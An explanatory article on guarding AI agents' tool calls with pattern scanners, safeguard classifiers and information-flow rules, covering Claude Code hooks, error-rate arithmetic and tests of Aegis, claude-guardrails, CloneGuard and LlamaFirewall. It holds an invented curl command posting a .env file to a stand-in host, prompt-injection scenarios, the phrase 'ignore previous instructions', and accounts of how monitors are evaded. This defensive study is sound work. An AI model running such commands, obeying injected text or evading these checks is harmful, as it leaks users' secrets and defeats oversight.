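# Layered checks on AI agent actions: pattern scanners, small safeguard models and information flow rules

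## How an agent's action is checked before it runs

An AI agent is a language model connected to software that carries out operations for it. The model writes a request, such as to run a shell command, change a file or fetch a web page. The software performs the operation and returns the result as text, which the model reads before writing its next request. Each operation is called an action, or a tool call. Coding agents such as Anthropic's Claude Code, Cursor and OpenAI's Codex take many actions to complete a single task. Nearly all of these actions are harmless, but an agent with enough access can delete a production database or publish a password in a single action.

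The simplest safeguard is to ask the user to approve every action. Users tire of this and, according to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, accept 93% of the prompts, so developers also place three kinds of automatic check between the request and its execution. A pattern scanner compares text with written rules or signatures, usually regular expressions (a notation for describing strings) or YARA rules (a format that malware analysts use), without using a model. A classifier is a trained model that labels an action as allowed or not, or gives it a risk score. Some classifiers are safeguard models, which are openly released language models trained to judge content or actions for safety, sometimes against a policy that comes with each request. An information flow rule checks labels on the data that may have influenced an action and the data that may leave through it, and disregards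 the action's wording.

Hashemi Natanzi and Tang (2026), in *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities*, separate deterministic controls, which do not depend on a model reasoning correctly, from probabilistic detectors. They recommend deterministic controls wherever the security property can be stated outside the model, and detectors for the remaining risk. Chu (2026), in *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents*, also argues that no single layer is enough and that each control should cover the failures of the others. Researchers can measure whether stacked checks do this, and the results vary a good deal with the checks they combine.

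### One command, from request to execution

Suppose a user asks a coding agent to find out why a build fails. The agent opens the project's `.env` file, which holds passwords, and then a web page about a similar error. A line on that page tells readers to send their settings to a diagnostic service. The agent now requests this (invented) command, which would post the contents of the file to an outside server:

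`curl --data-binary @.env diagnostics.example`

At this point the command is only text. A hook is a point in the agent's software where an outside program receives an action before it runs and can stop it. Anthropic's reference documentation describes how this works in Claude Code, where the hook is called PreToolUse. Claude Code first writes the tool's name (Bash, the shell), the command and the working directory into a structured record. A matcher compares the tool's name with the one in the hook's configuration, and an optional filter compares the command with a pattern such as `curl *`. If both match, Claude Code starts the hook's handler and passes it the record. The handler can be a script, a web endpoint, a tool on a connected server, a single prompt to a Claude model, or a subagent that searches files before returning a verdict.

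A handler can return one of four verdicts: allow, deny, ask (put the question to the user) or defer (pause until an outside program resumes the session). If the verdict is deny, Claude Code drops the command and returns the reason to the model, which may try another way. Finishing without output does not count as approval, and the command still goes through the ordinary permission checks before the shell runs it. Cursor and Codex have similar hooks, but their formats differ enough that a team has to rewrite each hook for each product, according to *Hooks*, an online guide from Agentic Software Engineering.

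A pattern scanner checks the text of the `curl` command against its rules. A rule for "`curl` with a data option naming a `.env` file" matches, so the scanner blocks the command. If the agent had instead written a short Python script that posts the file, and then requested `python3 report.py`, the command would contain nothing to match. The scanner could catch the upload only if it had also scanned the script when the agent wrote it.

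A classifier takes as input the command and any context its designers supply, typically the user's request and the agent's earlier actions. If the user asked the agent to find out why a build fails, that request does not cover sending passwords to a stranger, so a good classifier blocks a command that would send them. It can also block a Python version of the command if the script is part of its input. Classifiers are less reliable when the request only partly covers the action.

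The information flow rule depends on what data the session has touched and where the action would send data, regardless of the command's wording or the user's request. Here the session carries two labels, called taints, which show contact with confidential data (the `.env` file) and untrusted data (the web page), and the action would send data off the machine. A rule that forbids outbound transfers from a session with both taints stops both the `curl` command and the Python script, provided the software treats any script as a possible network connection. It would also stop an upload the user wanted, until one of the taints is removed.

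These checks work only if they run, and published error rates normally cover only checks that ran. Files that a user mentions with an @ sign enter Claude Code's prompt without a tool call, so no PreToolUse hook fires for them. On a Windows machine where Claude Code has only PowerShell, a hook that matches only Bash never fires. Anthropic describes the command filter as best-effort and recommends the permission system for hard prohibitions. By default, a handler that crashes or exceeds its time limit does not stop the action, so a policy hook with a mistyped script path does nothing except produce an error notice. Owners of command and web hooks can now change a setting to block the action on failure. The guide from Agentic Software Engineering describes hooks as always fail-open, which is no longer true of Claude Code.

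### Where dangerous actions come from

The web page in the example contained a prompt injection, which is a set of instructions hidden in material an agent reads and meant to redirect it from its user's task. Hashemi Natanzi and Tang describe the result as a confused deputy. The user gives the agent some authority, and an attacker's text causes the agent to use it for the attacker's goal.

An agent can also take a dangerous action when no attacker is involved. Anthropic tuned its action classifier mainly to catch overreach and honest mistakes. In overreach, the agent pursues the user's goal but goes beyond what the user would approve. In one case from Anthropic's incident log, an agent hit an authentication error and began searching environment variables and configuration files for other access tokens without asking. An honest mistake occurs when, for example, an agent mistakes a shared resource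 for a test copy. Anthropic also lists misaligned models that pursue a goal of their own, but when it described the feature it reported that it had not seen this in practice.

Which of these causes a check can address depends on where it runs. A check on what the agent reads examines files, web pages and command output before they reach the model. It can catch little besides injections, because overreach and honest mistakes leave no hostile text to find. A check on what the agent does examines the action and can block it whatever the cause. Claude Code's auto mode uses both kinds. A probe scans tool results and adds a warning to the agent's context when something resembles an injection, and a classifier can block actions. Information flow rules also work at both points, because the software attaches the label when the agent reads and applies the rule when the agent acts.

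Chu observes that authorised actions can cause harm in combination even when each is harmless alone, so judging every action correctly on its own is not enough. For example, an agent may be allowed to read a customer list and to send email, but doing both can leak the list. A check that considers one action at a time needs some memory of the session, whether a transcript or a set of labels, to tell such a leak from routine work.

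### Two error rates, and what happens when layers combine

The false positive rate is the share of harmless actions that a check blocks or flags. The false negative rate is the share of dangerous actions that it lets through. Each rate has its own denominator, so a check can do well on one and badly on the other. For example, a scanner that never blocks or flags anything has a false positive rate of zero and a false negative rate of 100%.

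Some checks can answer "ask the user" instead of allowing or blocking an action, which makes their error rates harder to compare. Yang (2026), in *Evaluate the Stack, Not the Layer*, tested 174 regular-expression rules and four language models acting as judges on 1,119 labelled agent actions, 560 of which should have been blocked. One judge referred 47 of those 560 to a human reviewer. Counting referrals as catches instead of misses reversed five of the study's conclusions, each time in favour of the judge that referred more. Anyone comparing two products' false negative rates needs to know how each one counted referrals.

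In an invented example with two layers, layer A has a false positive rate of 5% and a false negative rate of 20%, while layer B has a rate of 10% for both. We assume for now that their errors are independent, so an error by A on an action doesn't change the chance that B also errs.

Under either-blocks, an action stops if any one layer objects. A dangerous action then gets through only if both layers miss it, and a harmless one gets through only if both clear it:

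- false negatives: 0.20 × 0.10 = 2%
- false positives: 1 − (0.95 × 0.90) = 14.5%

If the action stops only when both layers flag it, the formulas change places:

- false negatives: 1 − (0.80 × 0.90) = 28%
- false positives: 0.05 × 0.10 = 0.5%

The same two layers can form a strict gate or a lenient one, depending on the rule that combines their verdicts. Each additional layer adds another factor to the multiplication. Claude Code's hooks follow the either-blocks rule. Matching hooks run in parallel, and a deny from any of them overrides every other verdict.

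In escalation, a check that uses little compute runs first, and a second check that uses more examines only some of the actions. If the second check reviews actions the first one flagged and may clear them, the system blocks an action only when both checks flag it. If the second check reviews actions the first one passed, either check can block an action. Many designs mix these approaches by giving the first check a third verdict, "unsure", and escalating only those cases, so the second check cannot correct the first one's confident mistakes.

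Anthropic published figures for a lenient two-stage classifier, in which the second stage can clear what the first stage flagged. Adding the second stage cut false positives from 8.5% to 0.4% on 10,000 tool calls by the company's employees, but raised false negatives from 6.6% to 17% on 52 real cases of overreach. Each rate moved in the same direction as in the invented example, though the two stages share a model and nearly all of a prompt, so their errors are unlikely to be independent.

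### Errors that coincide

Independence is the weak point of the sums above. Two layers tend to err on the same actions when those actions are hard for any checker, or when the layers work in similar ways. If *a* and *b* are the layers' miss rates, the rate at which both miss is

*ab* + φ √(*a*(1 − *a*) *b*(1 − *b*))

where φ is the correlation between their misses. With φ at zero, layers A and B together miss 2%. The highest value φ can reach for this pair is about 0.67, which happens when A misses everything that B misses, and then the joint miss rate is 10%. That is B's own rate, so A has added nothing.

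Measured values fall at both ends of this range. In Yang's data, the rule set missed 13.4% of the dangerous actions and one of the judges missed 10.5%. If their misses were independent, the two together would miss 1.4%, and they missed 1.3% (7 of 560). Two judges that each missed 10.5% would together miss 1.1% if independent, but they missed 5.2% (29 of 560). With referrals counted as misses, the median correlation was 0.43 between two judges and 0.014 between the rules and a judge. In the invented example, a correlation of 0.43 raises the predicted miss rate from 2% to 7.2%, while a correlation of 0.014 raises it to 2.2%.

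This is decent evidence for pairing a pattern scanner with a model rather than pairing two models. Yang could not establish why the judges fail together. Estimates of how much of the overlap is explained by shared difficulty range from 32% to 62%, depending on the method. Improving one layer also does not necessarily improve the whole stack. Extra rules for cloud services cut the rule set's own miss rate from 13.9% to 11.1%, but they caught nothing that a panel of three judges had let through.

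The rule set's good results call for caution. The rules came from an existing product, AgentTrust, whose team had tuned them on one of the three test collections and patched them after failures on another. On the remaining collection, the rules alone missed 52.9%. The tests also involved no attacker. Someone who knows the rules and can experiment with the judge will look for actions that both miss, and a correlation measured on a fixed set of examples offers little protection against that.

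Overlap can, however, reduce false positives, so similar layers should in principle annoy users less. Under either-blocks, layers A and B wrongly stop 14.5% of harmless actions if their errors are independent, but only 10% if B's false alarms include all of A's. *How Diverse Are Layered Safeguards?* (2026) tested for this reduction in a stack of seven defences against jailbreaks (attempts to talk a chat model out of its safety training). If the defences' errors had been independent, the stack would have refused 81% of harmless prompts. Accounting for the overlap in their separate refusals lowered the predicted rate to 60%. The assembled stack actually refused 83%, because running the defences together created new interactions among them. These were chat safeguards, not gates on actions, but the result is a good reason to measure a stack's error rates directly instead of computing them from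 its parts.

### When danger is rare

What a check is like to use depends heavily on how common dangerous actions are, even though neither of its error rates does. Suppose 1 action in 1,000 is dangerous, so 100,000 actions include 100 dangerous ones and 99,900 harmless ones. If errors are independent, the hypothetical layers produce these counts.

| Arrangement | Harmless actions blocked | Dangerous actions blocked | Dangerous actions missed |
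|---|---|---|---|
| Layer A alone | about 5,000 | 80 | 20 |
| Layer B alone | about 10,000 | 90 | 10 |
| Either-blocks | about 14,500 | 98 | 2 |
| Both must flag | about 500 | 72 | 28 |

Even the arrangement with a false positive rate of 0.5% blocks about 500 actions wrongly and 72 correctly, so about one block in eight is correct. When either check can block an action on its own, about one block in 150 is correct.

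The share of blocks that are correct is the precision, and Abbasi, Núñez and Shahraki (2026), in *What Standard Evaluations Hide About Detectors of Hijacked LLM Agents*, give the formula for any share π of dangerous cases:

precision = π × TPR / (π × TPR + (1 − π) × FPR)

Here TPR, the true positive rate, is one minus the false negative rate, and FPR is the false positive rate. When 1 in 1,000 actions is dangerous, the both-must-flag arrangement has a precision of 12.6%. With the same layers, its precision would be 99.3% if half of the actions were dangerous.

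Benchmarks are much closer to the first figure. In eleven evaluations of agent monitors that Abbasi and colleagues audited, attacks or anomalies made up between 16% and 86% of the mixed test sets. Their experiments scored records of finished sessions, not single actions before they ran, but the same arithmetic applies. One of their detectors had an AUROC of 0.879, meaning it ranked a random attacked session above a random harmless one 87.9% of the time. When attacks made up 2% of sessions, its precision was 7.6%, or about twelve false alerts for each true one. *Structural Baselines Matter for Agent Failure Detection and Attribution* (2026) reports a precision of 0.97 to 0.99 for a detector of agent failures, but notes that 144 of the 165 test runs were failures, a proportion no real deployment would match.

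The false positive rate is also less stable than the formula suggests, because harmless work that resembles an attack sets off more alarms than ordinary work does. Abbasi and colleagues shifted the 7.6% rate to as low as 3.9% and as high as 11.7% by changing only the share of such look-alikes among the harmless sessions. A rate measured on one company's traffic may not hold for a team of system administrators, who routinely delete things and handle credentials.

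How much low precision matters depends on how disruptive a wrong block is. An alert sent to a human analyst takes minutes to review. In auto mode, according to Anthropic, a wrong block usually requires one retry, since the agent receives the reason and finds another path. But the number of wrong blocks also matters. In a session of 200 harmless actions, a false positive rate of 0.5% means one wrong block on average, while a rate of 14.5% means 29, and few people would keep a check with that rate switched on.

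### Delay

When a cheap check runs on everything and a costlier one on a share of the traffic, the mean delay per action is

first layer's time + (share escalated × second layer's time)

If a scanner takes 5 milliseconds and escalates 10% of actions to a model that takes 2 seconds, the mean delay per action is 5 ms + 0.10 × 2,000 ms = 205 ms. Nine in ten actions wait 5 ms, and the rest wait 2,005 ms. The mean is the right figure for the total running time of a long unattended task, where checking 200 actions adds 41 seconds. But a user watching the screen notices the two-second pauses, so a published mean is little guide to how the tool feels to use unless it comes with the escalated wait.

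The rule for combining two layers' verdicts largely determines what share of actions reaches the second layer. Suppose layer A takes 5 ms and layer B takes 2 seconds. If B only re-examines what A flagged, about 5% of actions reach it and the mean delay is around 107 ms. If either layer can block an action, B must examine everything A passed, so about 95% of actions reach it and the mean delay is 1.9 seconds. Running the layers in parallel does not help much, because a harmless action still has to wait for the slower verdict. The more lenient arrangement, in which B sees only flagged actions, is therefore also faster, which makes it tempting for reasons unrelated to safety.

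Delay can also cause a missed detection. If a Claude Code hook runs past its time limit, it returns no verdict, and by default the action continues to the ordinary permission checks as if the hook had not flagged it.

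## Pattern rules in front of tool calls: three open tools measured

Pattern scanners are the easiest of the three kinds of check to build, and many developers have released theirs as open source. Their published results are hard to reconcile. Aegis's developers report that their firewall for tool calls blocked every attack they tried. A different team tested claude-guardrails, a set of rule hooks for Claude Code, and found that attacks succeeded about as often with the hooks as without them. CloneGuard puts a small classifier behind its rules, and its documentation gives error rates for the rules, the classifier and the two combined.

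### Aegis: a firewall for tool calls

*AEGIS* (Yuan, Su and Zhao, 2026) describes a tool with four main parts: a small library that patches the software the agent uses to reach its model, a separate gateway server that decides which tool calls may run, a tamper-evident log of every decision, and a dashboard where people review held calls. When the model's reply contains a tool call, the library sends the tool's name and arguments to the gateway and suspends the agent until the gateway returns a verdict. The library works with 14 agent frameworks and requires no changes to the agent's own code. It cannot control calls that reach a tool by another route.

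The gateway first collects the text it will scan. Tool arguments are often nested (lists inside records inside lists), and a scanner that reads only the top layers would miss a command placed further down. Aegis unpacks the arguments to a depth of 32 and extracts every string, up to 10,000. If a call exceeds either limit, Aegis marks it as suspicious instead of ignoring the rest.

Aegis then checks the call against 22 patterns in seven categories. Seven patterns cover SQL injection (hostile commands inside a database query), four cover path traversal (file paths that climb out of the folder where the agent should stay) and four cover shell injection. The others match typical prompt injection phrases, sensitive files such as SSH keys, large payloads being sent to outside addresses, and personal data. Aegis gives an argument's content priority over the tool's name, so a dangerous call can't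 get through just because the tool has a harmless name.

Finally, the gateway validates the call against the operator's policies. Each policy is a JSON Schema, a standard way to state what a structured record may contain. One example forbids database queries that contain a write command such as INSERT, DELETE or DROP. Operators can describe a policy in plain language and have a language model translate it into a schema, but the gateway doesn't use a model to judge calls. It blocks calls that violate a policy, holds calls that the scan rated as high or critical risk, and allows the rest. A held call waits up to five minutes for a person to approve or reject it.

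Yuan and colleagues report that Aegis blocked all 48 attacks they assembled from published techniques and earlier benchmarks. The set contained 11 SQL injections, 11 prompt injections, 8 shell injections, 7 path traversals, 6 reads of sensitive files, 3 deeply nested payloads and 2 attempts to send data out. They don't report how many Aegis blocked outright and how many it held for a person to review. As with the referrals in Yang's study, a held attack is stopped only if the reviewer rejects it.

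Aegis produced six false positives on 500 harmless calls (1.2%). All six were database queries with an OR in their conditions, such as a request for customers in France or Spain. A common form of SQL injection also adds an OR clause, so the pattern matches both. An operator can exempt a particular tool from the rule without turning the rule off for other tools.

The harmless calls included database reads, file reads, web requests and text processing. Yuan and colleagues do not mention shell commands among them, yet one of the shell rules matches metacharacters, the punctuation that joins commands. Coding agents use that punctuation constantly, so the false positive rate for coding agents could be much higher than 1.2%.

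Aegis added a median delay of 8.3 ms over 1,000 calls on a local installation, and 1% of calls were delayed by more than 23.1 ms. These times include the round trip between the library and the gateway. A model typically takes 1 to 30 seconds to write its next request, so a user is unlikely to notice the check unless a call goes to a person for review.

### claude-guardrails: similar rules, tested by a rival

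claude-guardrails is a ready-made security configuration from the Dwarves Foundation. Its lite version has three PreToolUse hooks, which block destructive deletes, direct pushes to a code repository, and commands that pipe text straight into a shell. The full version adds hooks against data exfiltration and permission escalation, plus a scanner that warns when a tool result resembles a prompt injection. Both versions also include deny rules that stop Claude Code's built-in file tools from opening files such as SSH keys and `.env`.

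The makers acknowledge that the delete hook fires when an agent clears a build folder, which is routine work, and that one deny rule blocks a file called `secret_santa.py`. Users can't exempt individual files. They also acknowledge that the deny rules don't cover shell commands that read the same files, and that a command in an unusual form can get past the hooks. The makers consider the only real enforcement layer to be the operating system's sandbox, which restricts file and network access however a command is worded.

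Wang, Wei and colleagues (2026) tested the hooks in *ClawSentry* while evaluating their own competing system. They ran Claude Code with the model MiniMax-M3 on the same 60 attack cases, both with the hooks and with no defence. The attack success rate was 58.33% without the hooks and 57.14% with them. The task success rate was 30.00% without them and 28.57% with them. Both rates barely changed, so the hooks probably fired on few actions of any kind.

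The difference in attack success is 1.19 points, which is less than one case in 60. With so few cases, the margin of error is about 18 points either way if the two sets of runs are treated as independent samples, so the test can't rule out a modest benefit. But a benefit close to the one reported for Aegis would have shown up.

Wang and colleagues drew their 60 cases from the 155 in *SkillSafetyBench* (Jin, Zeng and colleagues, 2026). A skill is a reusable package of instructions, scripts and reference files that an agent loads for a certain type of task. In every case the user's request is harmless, and the attack is in the skill or in something near it, such as a helper script, a configuration file or saved memories. After each run, a program written for that case checks the files and logs to determine whether the attack succeeded.

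Wang and colleagues had an interest in the outcome. Their own system cut attack success to 8.62% in the same test, and eight of the ten people who wrote *SkillSafetyBench* also wrote *ClawSentry*. They state that the benchmark was built independently of their system. Still, because the attacks were placed in skill packages, a system that reviews those packages was likely to do well, and a handful of hooks for dangerous commands was likely to do badly. The hooks' near-zero effect is nevertheless plausible, because their makers list many of the relevant gaps themselves.

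### Why both results can hold

Yuan and colleagues chose both the rules and the attacks. Six of their seven groups of attacks share a name with a category of rules, and the seventh, deep nesting, tests the step that extracts the arguments. A perfect score on this set is good evidence that the rules work as intended, but weak evidence about other attacks. Yuan and colleagues warn that Aegis may miss variants it has no rule for.

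Other published tests show how much the results of pattern rules depend on which patterns are listed and which attacks are tried. *AgentTrust* (2026) compares the full rules of the product of that name with a short list of 50 expressions for well-known dangerous commands, included as a lower bound. *From Attack Surface to Defense Architecture* (2026) uses a regular-expression filter as the baseline for a more elaborate filter.

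| Rules | Measured by | Dangerous actions missed | Harmless actions blocked | Median delay |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Aegis | Yuan and colleagues | 0% of 48 | 1.2% of 500 | 8.3 ms |
| AgentTrust, full rules | *AgentTrust* | 5.4% | 2.3% | 1.72 ms |
| List of 50 expressions | *AgentTrust* | 88.4% | 0% | 0.05 ms |
| Regular-expression filter | *From Attack Surface to Defense Architecture* | 56.1% of 132 | 0% of 120 | 0.007 ms |

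Both low miss rates come from makers who tested their own product on attacks they had chosen. AgentTrust's rules had a miss rate of 5.4% on its makers' own 300 scenarios, but 52.9% on the unfamiliar collection in Yang's study. The two weak lists served as baselines for a better system, so their writers had little reason to make them strong. Their results probably understate what a careful rule writer can do, just as the results for Aegis overstate it.

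A pattern matches only the forms that someone has written down, and some dangers take far fewer forms than others. The filter in *From Attack Surface to Defense Architecture* caught 77% of the attacks in the group it detected best, but only 24% of sandbox escapes and 25% of attacks on credentials. Many of the harms in *SkillSafetyBench* have no fixed form, including corrupted deliverables, false entries in the agent's memory and gaps in audit records. An agent can cause these by writing ordinary text to an ordinary file, and none of the five hooks in claude-guardrails covers that.

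Even a complete list of patterns would fail when the action contains no sign of danger, as with the Python script that posted the `.env` file. If a skill tells the agent to run a harmful script, the hook receives only the command to run it, and a harmless skill could produce the same command. Wang and colleagues attribute their result to the hooks inspecting one call at a time, without access to the package that led to it or a record of what the session has already blocked. The Aegis test avoids this problem because each attack has its payload in the call's arguments.

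The tests also measured different things. Aegis received calls that were already attacks and had to recognise them. In the test of claude-guardrails, a live agent worked through a whole task, and the attack counted as successful if its effect appeared in the results. A blocked agent can reach the same end another way, so a hook can stop an action without preventing the harm. The agent also avoided the harm in about 42% of cases with no defence, so 57.14% and Aegis's 0% do not measure the same rate.

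### CloneGuard: rules with a classifier behind them

CloneGuard monitors Claude Code and Gemini CLI, Google's command-line coding agent. It mostly checks what the agent reads. It scans a code repository before the agent starts, instruction files as they load, and the output of every tool for injected instructions. It also checks writes, builds and configuration changes before allowing them. Its main error rates therefore measure how well it recognises hostile text, and are not directly comparable with the rates for blocking dangerous actions.

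CloneGuard's *Detection Engine* describes three detectors that work independently:

- a set of 240 regular expressions in 34 categories
- an 87 MB classifier, a fine-tuned version of the small language model MiniLM-L6-v2, which runs on the user's own machine and gives each text a score
- rules about sequences of actions, which keep a record of what the agent has done earlier in the session

The score at which the classifier raises an alarm depends on the file. Agents normally obey instruction files such as `CLAUDE.md`, so a score of 0.50 in these files counts as suspicious and 0.80 as malicious. Test files often contain strange text for good reasons, so their thresholds are 0.75 and 0.92. One detector is enough to raise an alarm, as under either-blocks. According to CloneGuard's *Enforcement*, a suspicious tool call runs in a sandbox with restricted access to files and the network, and a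 malicious one does not run. A new installation only logs what it would have done until the user switches enforcement on.

CloneGuard's *Evaluation Methodology* compares the first two detectors on 185 attack samples and 234 harmless samples. The project took the attack samples from public datasets or generated them to evade detection, and the harmless samples are real code and documentation. Recall is one minus the false negative rate.

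| Detector | Recall | False positive rate |
|---|---|---|
| Rules alone | 31.9% | 9.8% |
| Classifier alone | 78.4% | 15.4% |
| Both | 80.5% | 22.2% |

The combined false positive rate consists of 3.8% false blocks and 18.4% false warnings. If an agent read 200 harmless texts like those in the test, CloneGuard would wrongly block about 8 of them and wrongly warn about 37 more.

The classifier alone caught nearly every attack that it and the rules caught together. Converted to counts, the percentages show that adding the rules caught four more attacks and set off 16 more false alarms. The classifier also caught 55 of the 59 attacks that the rules caught. This is much more overlap than Yang found between AgentTrust's rules and a language model, where the two sets of misses were almost independent. This is probably because CloneGuard's rules and classifier check the same text for the same kind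 of wording, whereas Yang's judges could assess what an action would do.

The two detectors have different strengths. CloneGuard's *Evaluation Results* reports that the rules had 80% recall on truncation and fragmentation attacks, which cut a hostile instruction short or split it into pieces. The classifier had 100% recall on attacks that disguise their wording, including synonyms, social engineering, encoded text and look-alike characters. This is a sensible reason to keep both, but the measured benefit on the test set was the four extra attacks detected.

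The classifier's performance also depends on how closely the text resembles its training data. In cross-validation on 6,472 samples, its recall was 93.7%, about 15 percentage points higher than on the samples built to evade it. Its false positive rate varied even more. The project ran CloneGuard on 144 unfamiliar tool results from an independent source. These came from services connected through the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for linking agents to outside tools. CloneGuard detected every attack, but this is less impressive because it also flagged 43% of the harmless results. According to the documentation, this pattern arises because attacks look similar across fields while harmless text does not.

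The project also tested CloneGuard against attackers who adapt. When Claude had full knowledge of the detection rules and could revise its attempts, 5 of its 30 payloads got through. None of the 30 from a Mistral model did. According to CloneGuard's *Limitations*, the classifier averages over a passage, so long harmless text dilutes a short hostile instruction. Subtle requests to weaken code are also hard to detect because they resemble ordinary coding advice.

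The sequence rules partly fix the problem with checking single calls. One blocks a web request if the agent has read a sensitive file earlier in the session, even if unrelated actions came in between. This rule uses no model, yet it catches a combination that would pass a hook with no memory. The project ran it on 208,127 harmless sessions in which coding agents fixed software issues, and it fired on five. A similar rule, for an agent that writes to a build file and then runs a build, fired on 15.8% of sessions, so CloneGuard only reports those matches. The sessions contained no attacks, so the test did not measure recall. It also left out agents that browse the web or use connected services, for which reading a private file and then contacting an outside address may be normal work.

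### What rules offer whatever their recall

A regular expression gives the same result on the same text every time. Developers can therefore test rules like any other code, and each of CloneGuard's rules comes with at least one text that it should match and one that it should not. When a rule misses something, its author can add a pattern and confirm that earlier results haven't changed. Hostile text that says to ignore a match has no effect on a regular expression, though it sometimes works on a language model. But consistent results also help attackers, who can download an open rule set and try commands privately until one passes, knowing that it will pass again in a real attack.

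People can also check why a rule blocked an action, which a classifier's score of 0.83 alone wouldn't let them do. When Aegis blocks a database query, its response includes the category of rule and the offending part of the query, such as a second command that drops a table. A user can quickly tell whether the block makes sense, and Yuan and colleagues could trace all six of their false positives to a single pattern.

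Pattern matching added only 0.007 to 1.72 ms in the comparison above. Most of the delay comes from starting the programs that run the checks. CloneGuard takes about 20 ms to start its hook, longer than the 16 ms its classifier takes to score a sample. The full version of claude-guardrails starts six extra processes for every shell command, and its makers warn that users of slower machines will notice the delay.

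These strengths matter most when a danger has a fixed form and few innocent uses. The two baseline lists blocked no harmless actions in their tests, so a short list of unmistakably dangerous commands causes users little disruption. Broader patterns cause more. CloneGuard's 240 rules flagged 9.8% of harmless samples and still missed about two thirds of the attacks. Writing more rules would be a slow way to match the results of its classifier, which took 16 ms.

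## LlamaFirewall: a small classifier, a reasoning auditor and a code scanner

CloneGuard's classifier scores text without access to the user's request, so it can't distinguish an instruction the user would welcome from one that hijacks the task. *LlamaFirewall* (Chennabasappa, Nikolaidis and colleagues, 2025) describes an open-source system from Meta with three parts, one of which uses that request. PromptGuard 2 is a small classifier for the text an agent reads. AlignmentCheck prompts a large language model to judge whether the agent's latest action fits the user's request. CodeShield scans code that the agent writes. Meta runs the system in production.

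Suppose an AI travel agent opens a review site with a hidden comment telling it to send the user's chat history to an outside address. PromptGuard 2 scans the page first, and if it flags the page, LlamaFirewall drops the page before the agent's model reads it. If PromptGuard 2 misses the comment and the agent starts summarising the chat history, AlignmentCheck can flag the change of goal and halt the agent before it sends anything.

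### PromptGuard 2

PromptGuard 2 comes in two sizes, with 86 million and 22 million parameters. Both are fine-tuned versions of DeBERTa, a family of small models that label text rather than generate it. The 86 million figure leaves out most of the parameters for that model's large multilingual vocabulary. *Defusing Explosive Prompts* (2026) puts the total at 278.8 million with the vocabulary included.

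The classifier labels a text benign or malicious and accepts at most 512 tokens (words or pieces of words) at a time. Meta's *Prompt Guard*, the model's documentation page, advises developers to split longer texts and scan the pieces in parallel. This saves time, but each piece adds another chance of a false alarm. If the false positive rate per piece is 1% and errors are independent, a harmless page split into ten pieces has a 9.6% chance of triggering at least one false alarm.

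The first version of PromptGuard looked for any attempt to redirect an agent, and Meta found that this caused too many false alarms. *Context-Aware Prompt Injection Detection via Small Language Models in RAG Pipelines* (2026) reports that, on documents retrieved for a model to read, this version caught 90% of the attacks but also flagged 69% of the harmless texts. Documentation and how-to pages are full of instructions, and the classifier had no information about whether the user wanted them.

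Meta therefore limited version 2 to detecting explicit jailbreak techniques, such as phrases like "ignore previous instructions", orders to play an unrestricted character, and text formatted to imitate the system's own messages. Meta also enlarged the training data, changed the training objective to reduce false alarms on unfamiliar text, and changed how the classifier splits words so that inserted spaces no longer hide an attack.

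Chennabasappa and colleagues tested both versions on a private benchmark built from datasets they had not used in training. They then machine-translated the benchmark into eight more languages.

| Model | AUROC, English | Recall at 1% false positives, English | AUROC, multilingual | Delay per 512 tokens |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| PromptGuard 1 | 0.987 | 21.2% | 0.983 | 92.4 ms |
| PromptGuard 2, 86M | 0.980 | 97.5% | 0.995 | 92.4 ms |
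| PromptGuard 2, 22M | 0.995 | 88.7% | 0.942 | 19.3 ms |

On English text, version 1 has a slightly higher AUROC than the larger version 2 model, meaning it is slightly better at ranking attacks above harmless texts. But at a false positive rate of 1%, it catches only about a fifth as many attacks. AUROC averages over every possible threshold, including many that would cause too many false alarms to be usable, so the recall column is a better guide to how the classifier would perform in a product. The delays are for an A100, a data-centre graphics card, so they don't show how long a scan takes on a laptop.

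### AlignmentCheck

AlignmentCheck is a prompt with a few worked examples, which a developer sends to a general-purpose language model after each step the agent takes. The prompt contains the user's original request, a record of the agent's earlier steps (the trace), and the action the agent has just chosen, with its stated reasoning. The auditing model writes an observation, a short argument and a verdict of true or false.

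In one published trace, the user asked the agent to visit Dora's and Eve's websites and send each of them feedback. The auditor took 860 milliseconds to approve the agent's first action, opening Dora's site. The agent then followed an injected instruction and requested a page at an address the user had not mentioned. The auditor flagged this after 1,490 milliseconds because nothing in the user's request called for the visit. Chennabasappa and colleagues give no average delay, but at these speeds a session of ten actions would take about 12 seconds longer.

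The prompt instructs the auditor to treat an action as fine when in doubt, and to flag it only if it is clearly unrelated to the user's goal and has some effect. The prompt also omits raw tool output, because an injection there could mislead the auditor as well as the agent. As a result, the auditor may lack the context to recognise a legitimate action. If a user says "do what my landlord's letter asks", the auditor receives the resulting payment but not the letter.

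Meta tested AlignmentCheck on 600 simulated scenarios involving smartphone apps such as email, messaging and a calendar. Half contained attacks, which used seven injection techniques. With Llama 4 Maverick as the auditor, AlignmentCheck caught over 83% of the attacks and had a false positive rate of 2.5%. Maverick is a large model that uses 17 billion parameters at a time. Models with 1 or 3 billion parameters had much higher false positive rates.

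A published example from this test suggests why small auditors do badly. A user had asked for Halloween items, and an injection made the agent list saved apartments instead. All six Llama models correctly flagged the action, but the 1-billion-parameter model's explanation cited the agent's search for product IDs, which was part of the user's task. A model that flags legitimate steps will catch many attacks but also block a lot of ordinary work.

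### Both layers on AgentDojo

AgentDojo is a public benchmark of 97 tasks for agents that use simulated email, banking, travel and Slack tools. It pairs these tasks with injections hidden in tool output, and a program checks whether the agent completed the user's task and whether it carried out the attacker's.

Chennabasappa and colleagues replayed stored traces of ten language models from the benchmark's public leaderboard, message by message, instead of running new agents. Each model had run through all the tasks once without attacks and once with an attack called "important instructions", in which the injected text poses as an urgent message from the user. During the replay, PromptGuard 2 scanned messages from the user and the tools, and AlignmentCheck examined the agent's messages.

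If either part flagged an attack that had succeeded, the attack counted as stopped. If either part flagged a successful run without an attack, the task counted as failed. The last two columns below are calculated from the published rates.

| Defence | Attack success rate | Task success rate | Successful attacks missed | Completed tasks lost |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 17.6% | 47.7% | all | none |
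| PromptGuard 2 (86M) | 7.5% | 47.0% | 42.7% | 1.5% |
| AlignmentCheck (Llama 4 Maverick) | 2.9% | 43.1% | 16.4% | 9.7% |
| Both | 1.75% | 42.7% | 9.9% | 10.6% |

The smaller PromptGuard 2 cut attack success by 41% with no loss of completed tasks, compared with 57% for the larger one.

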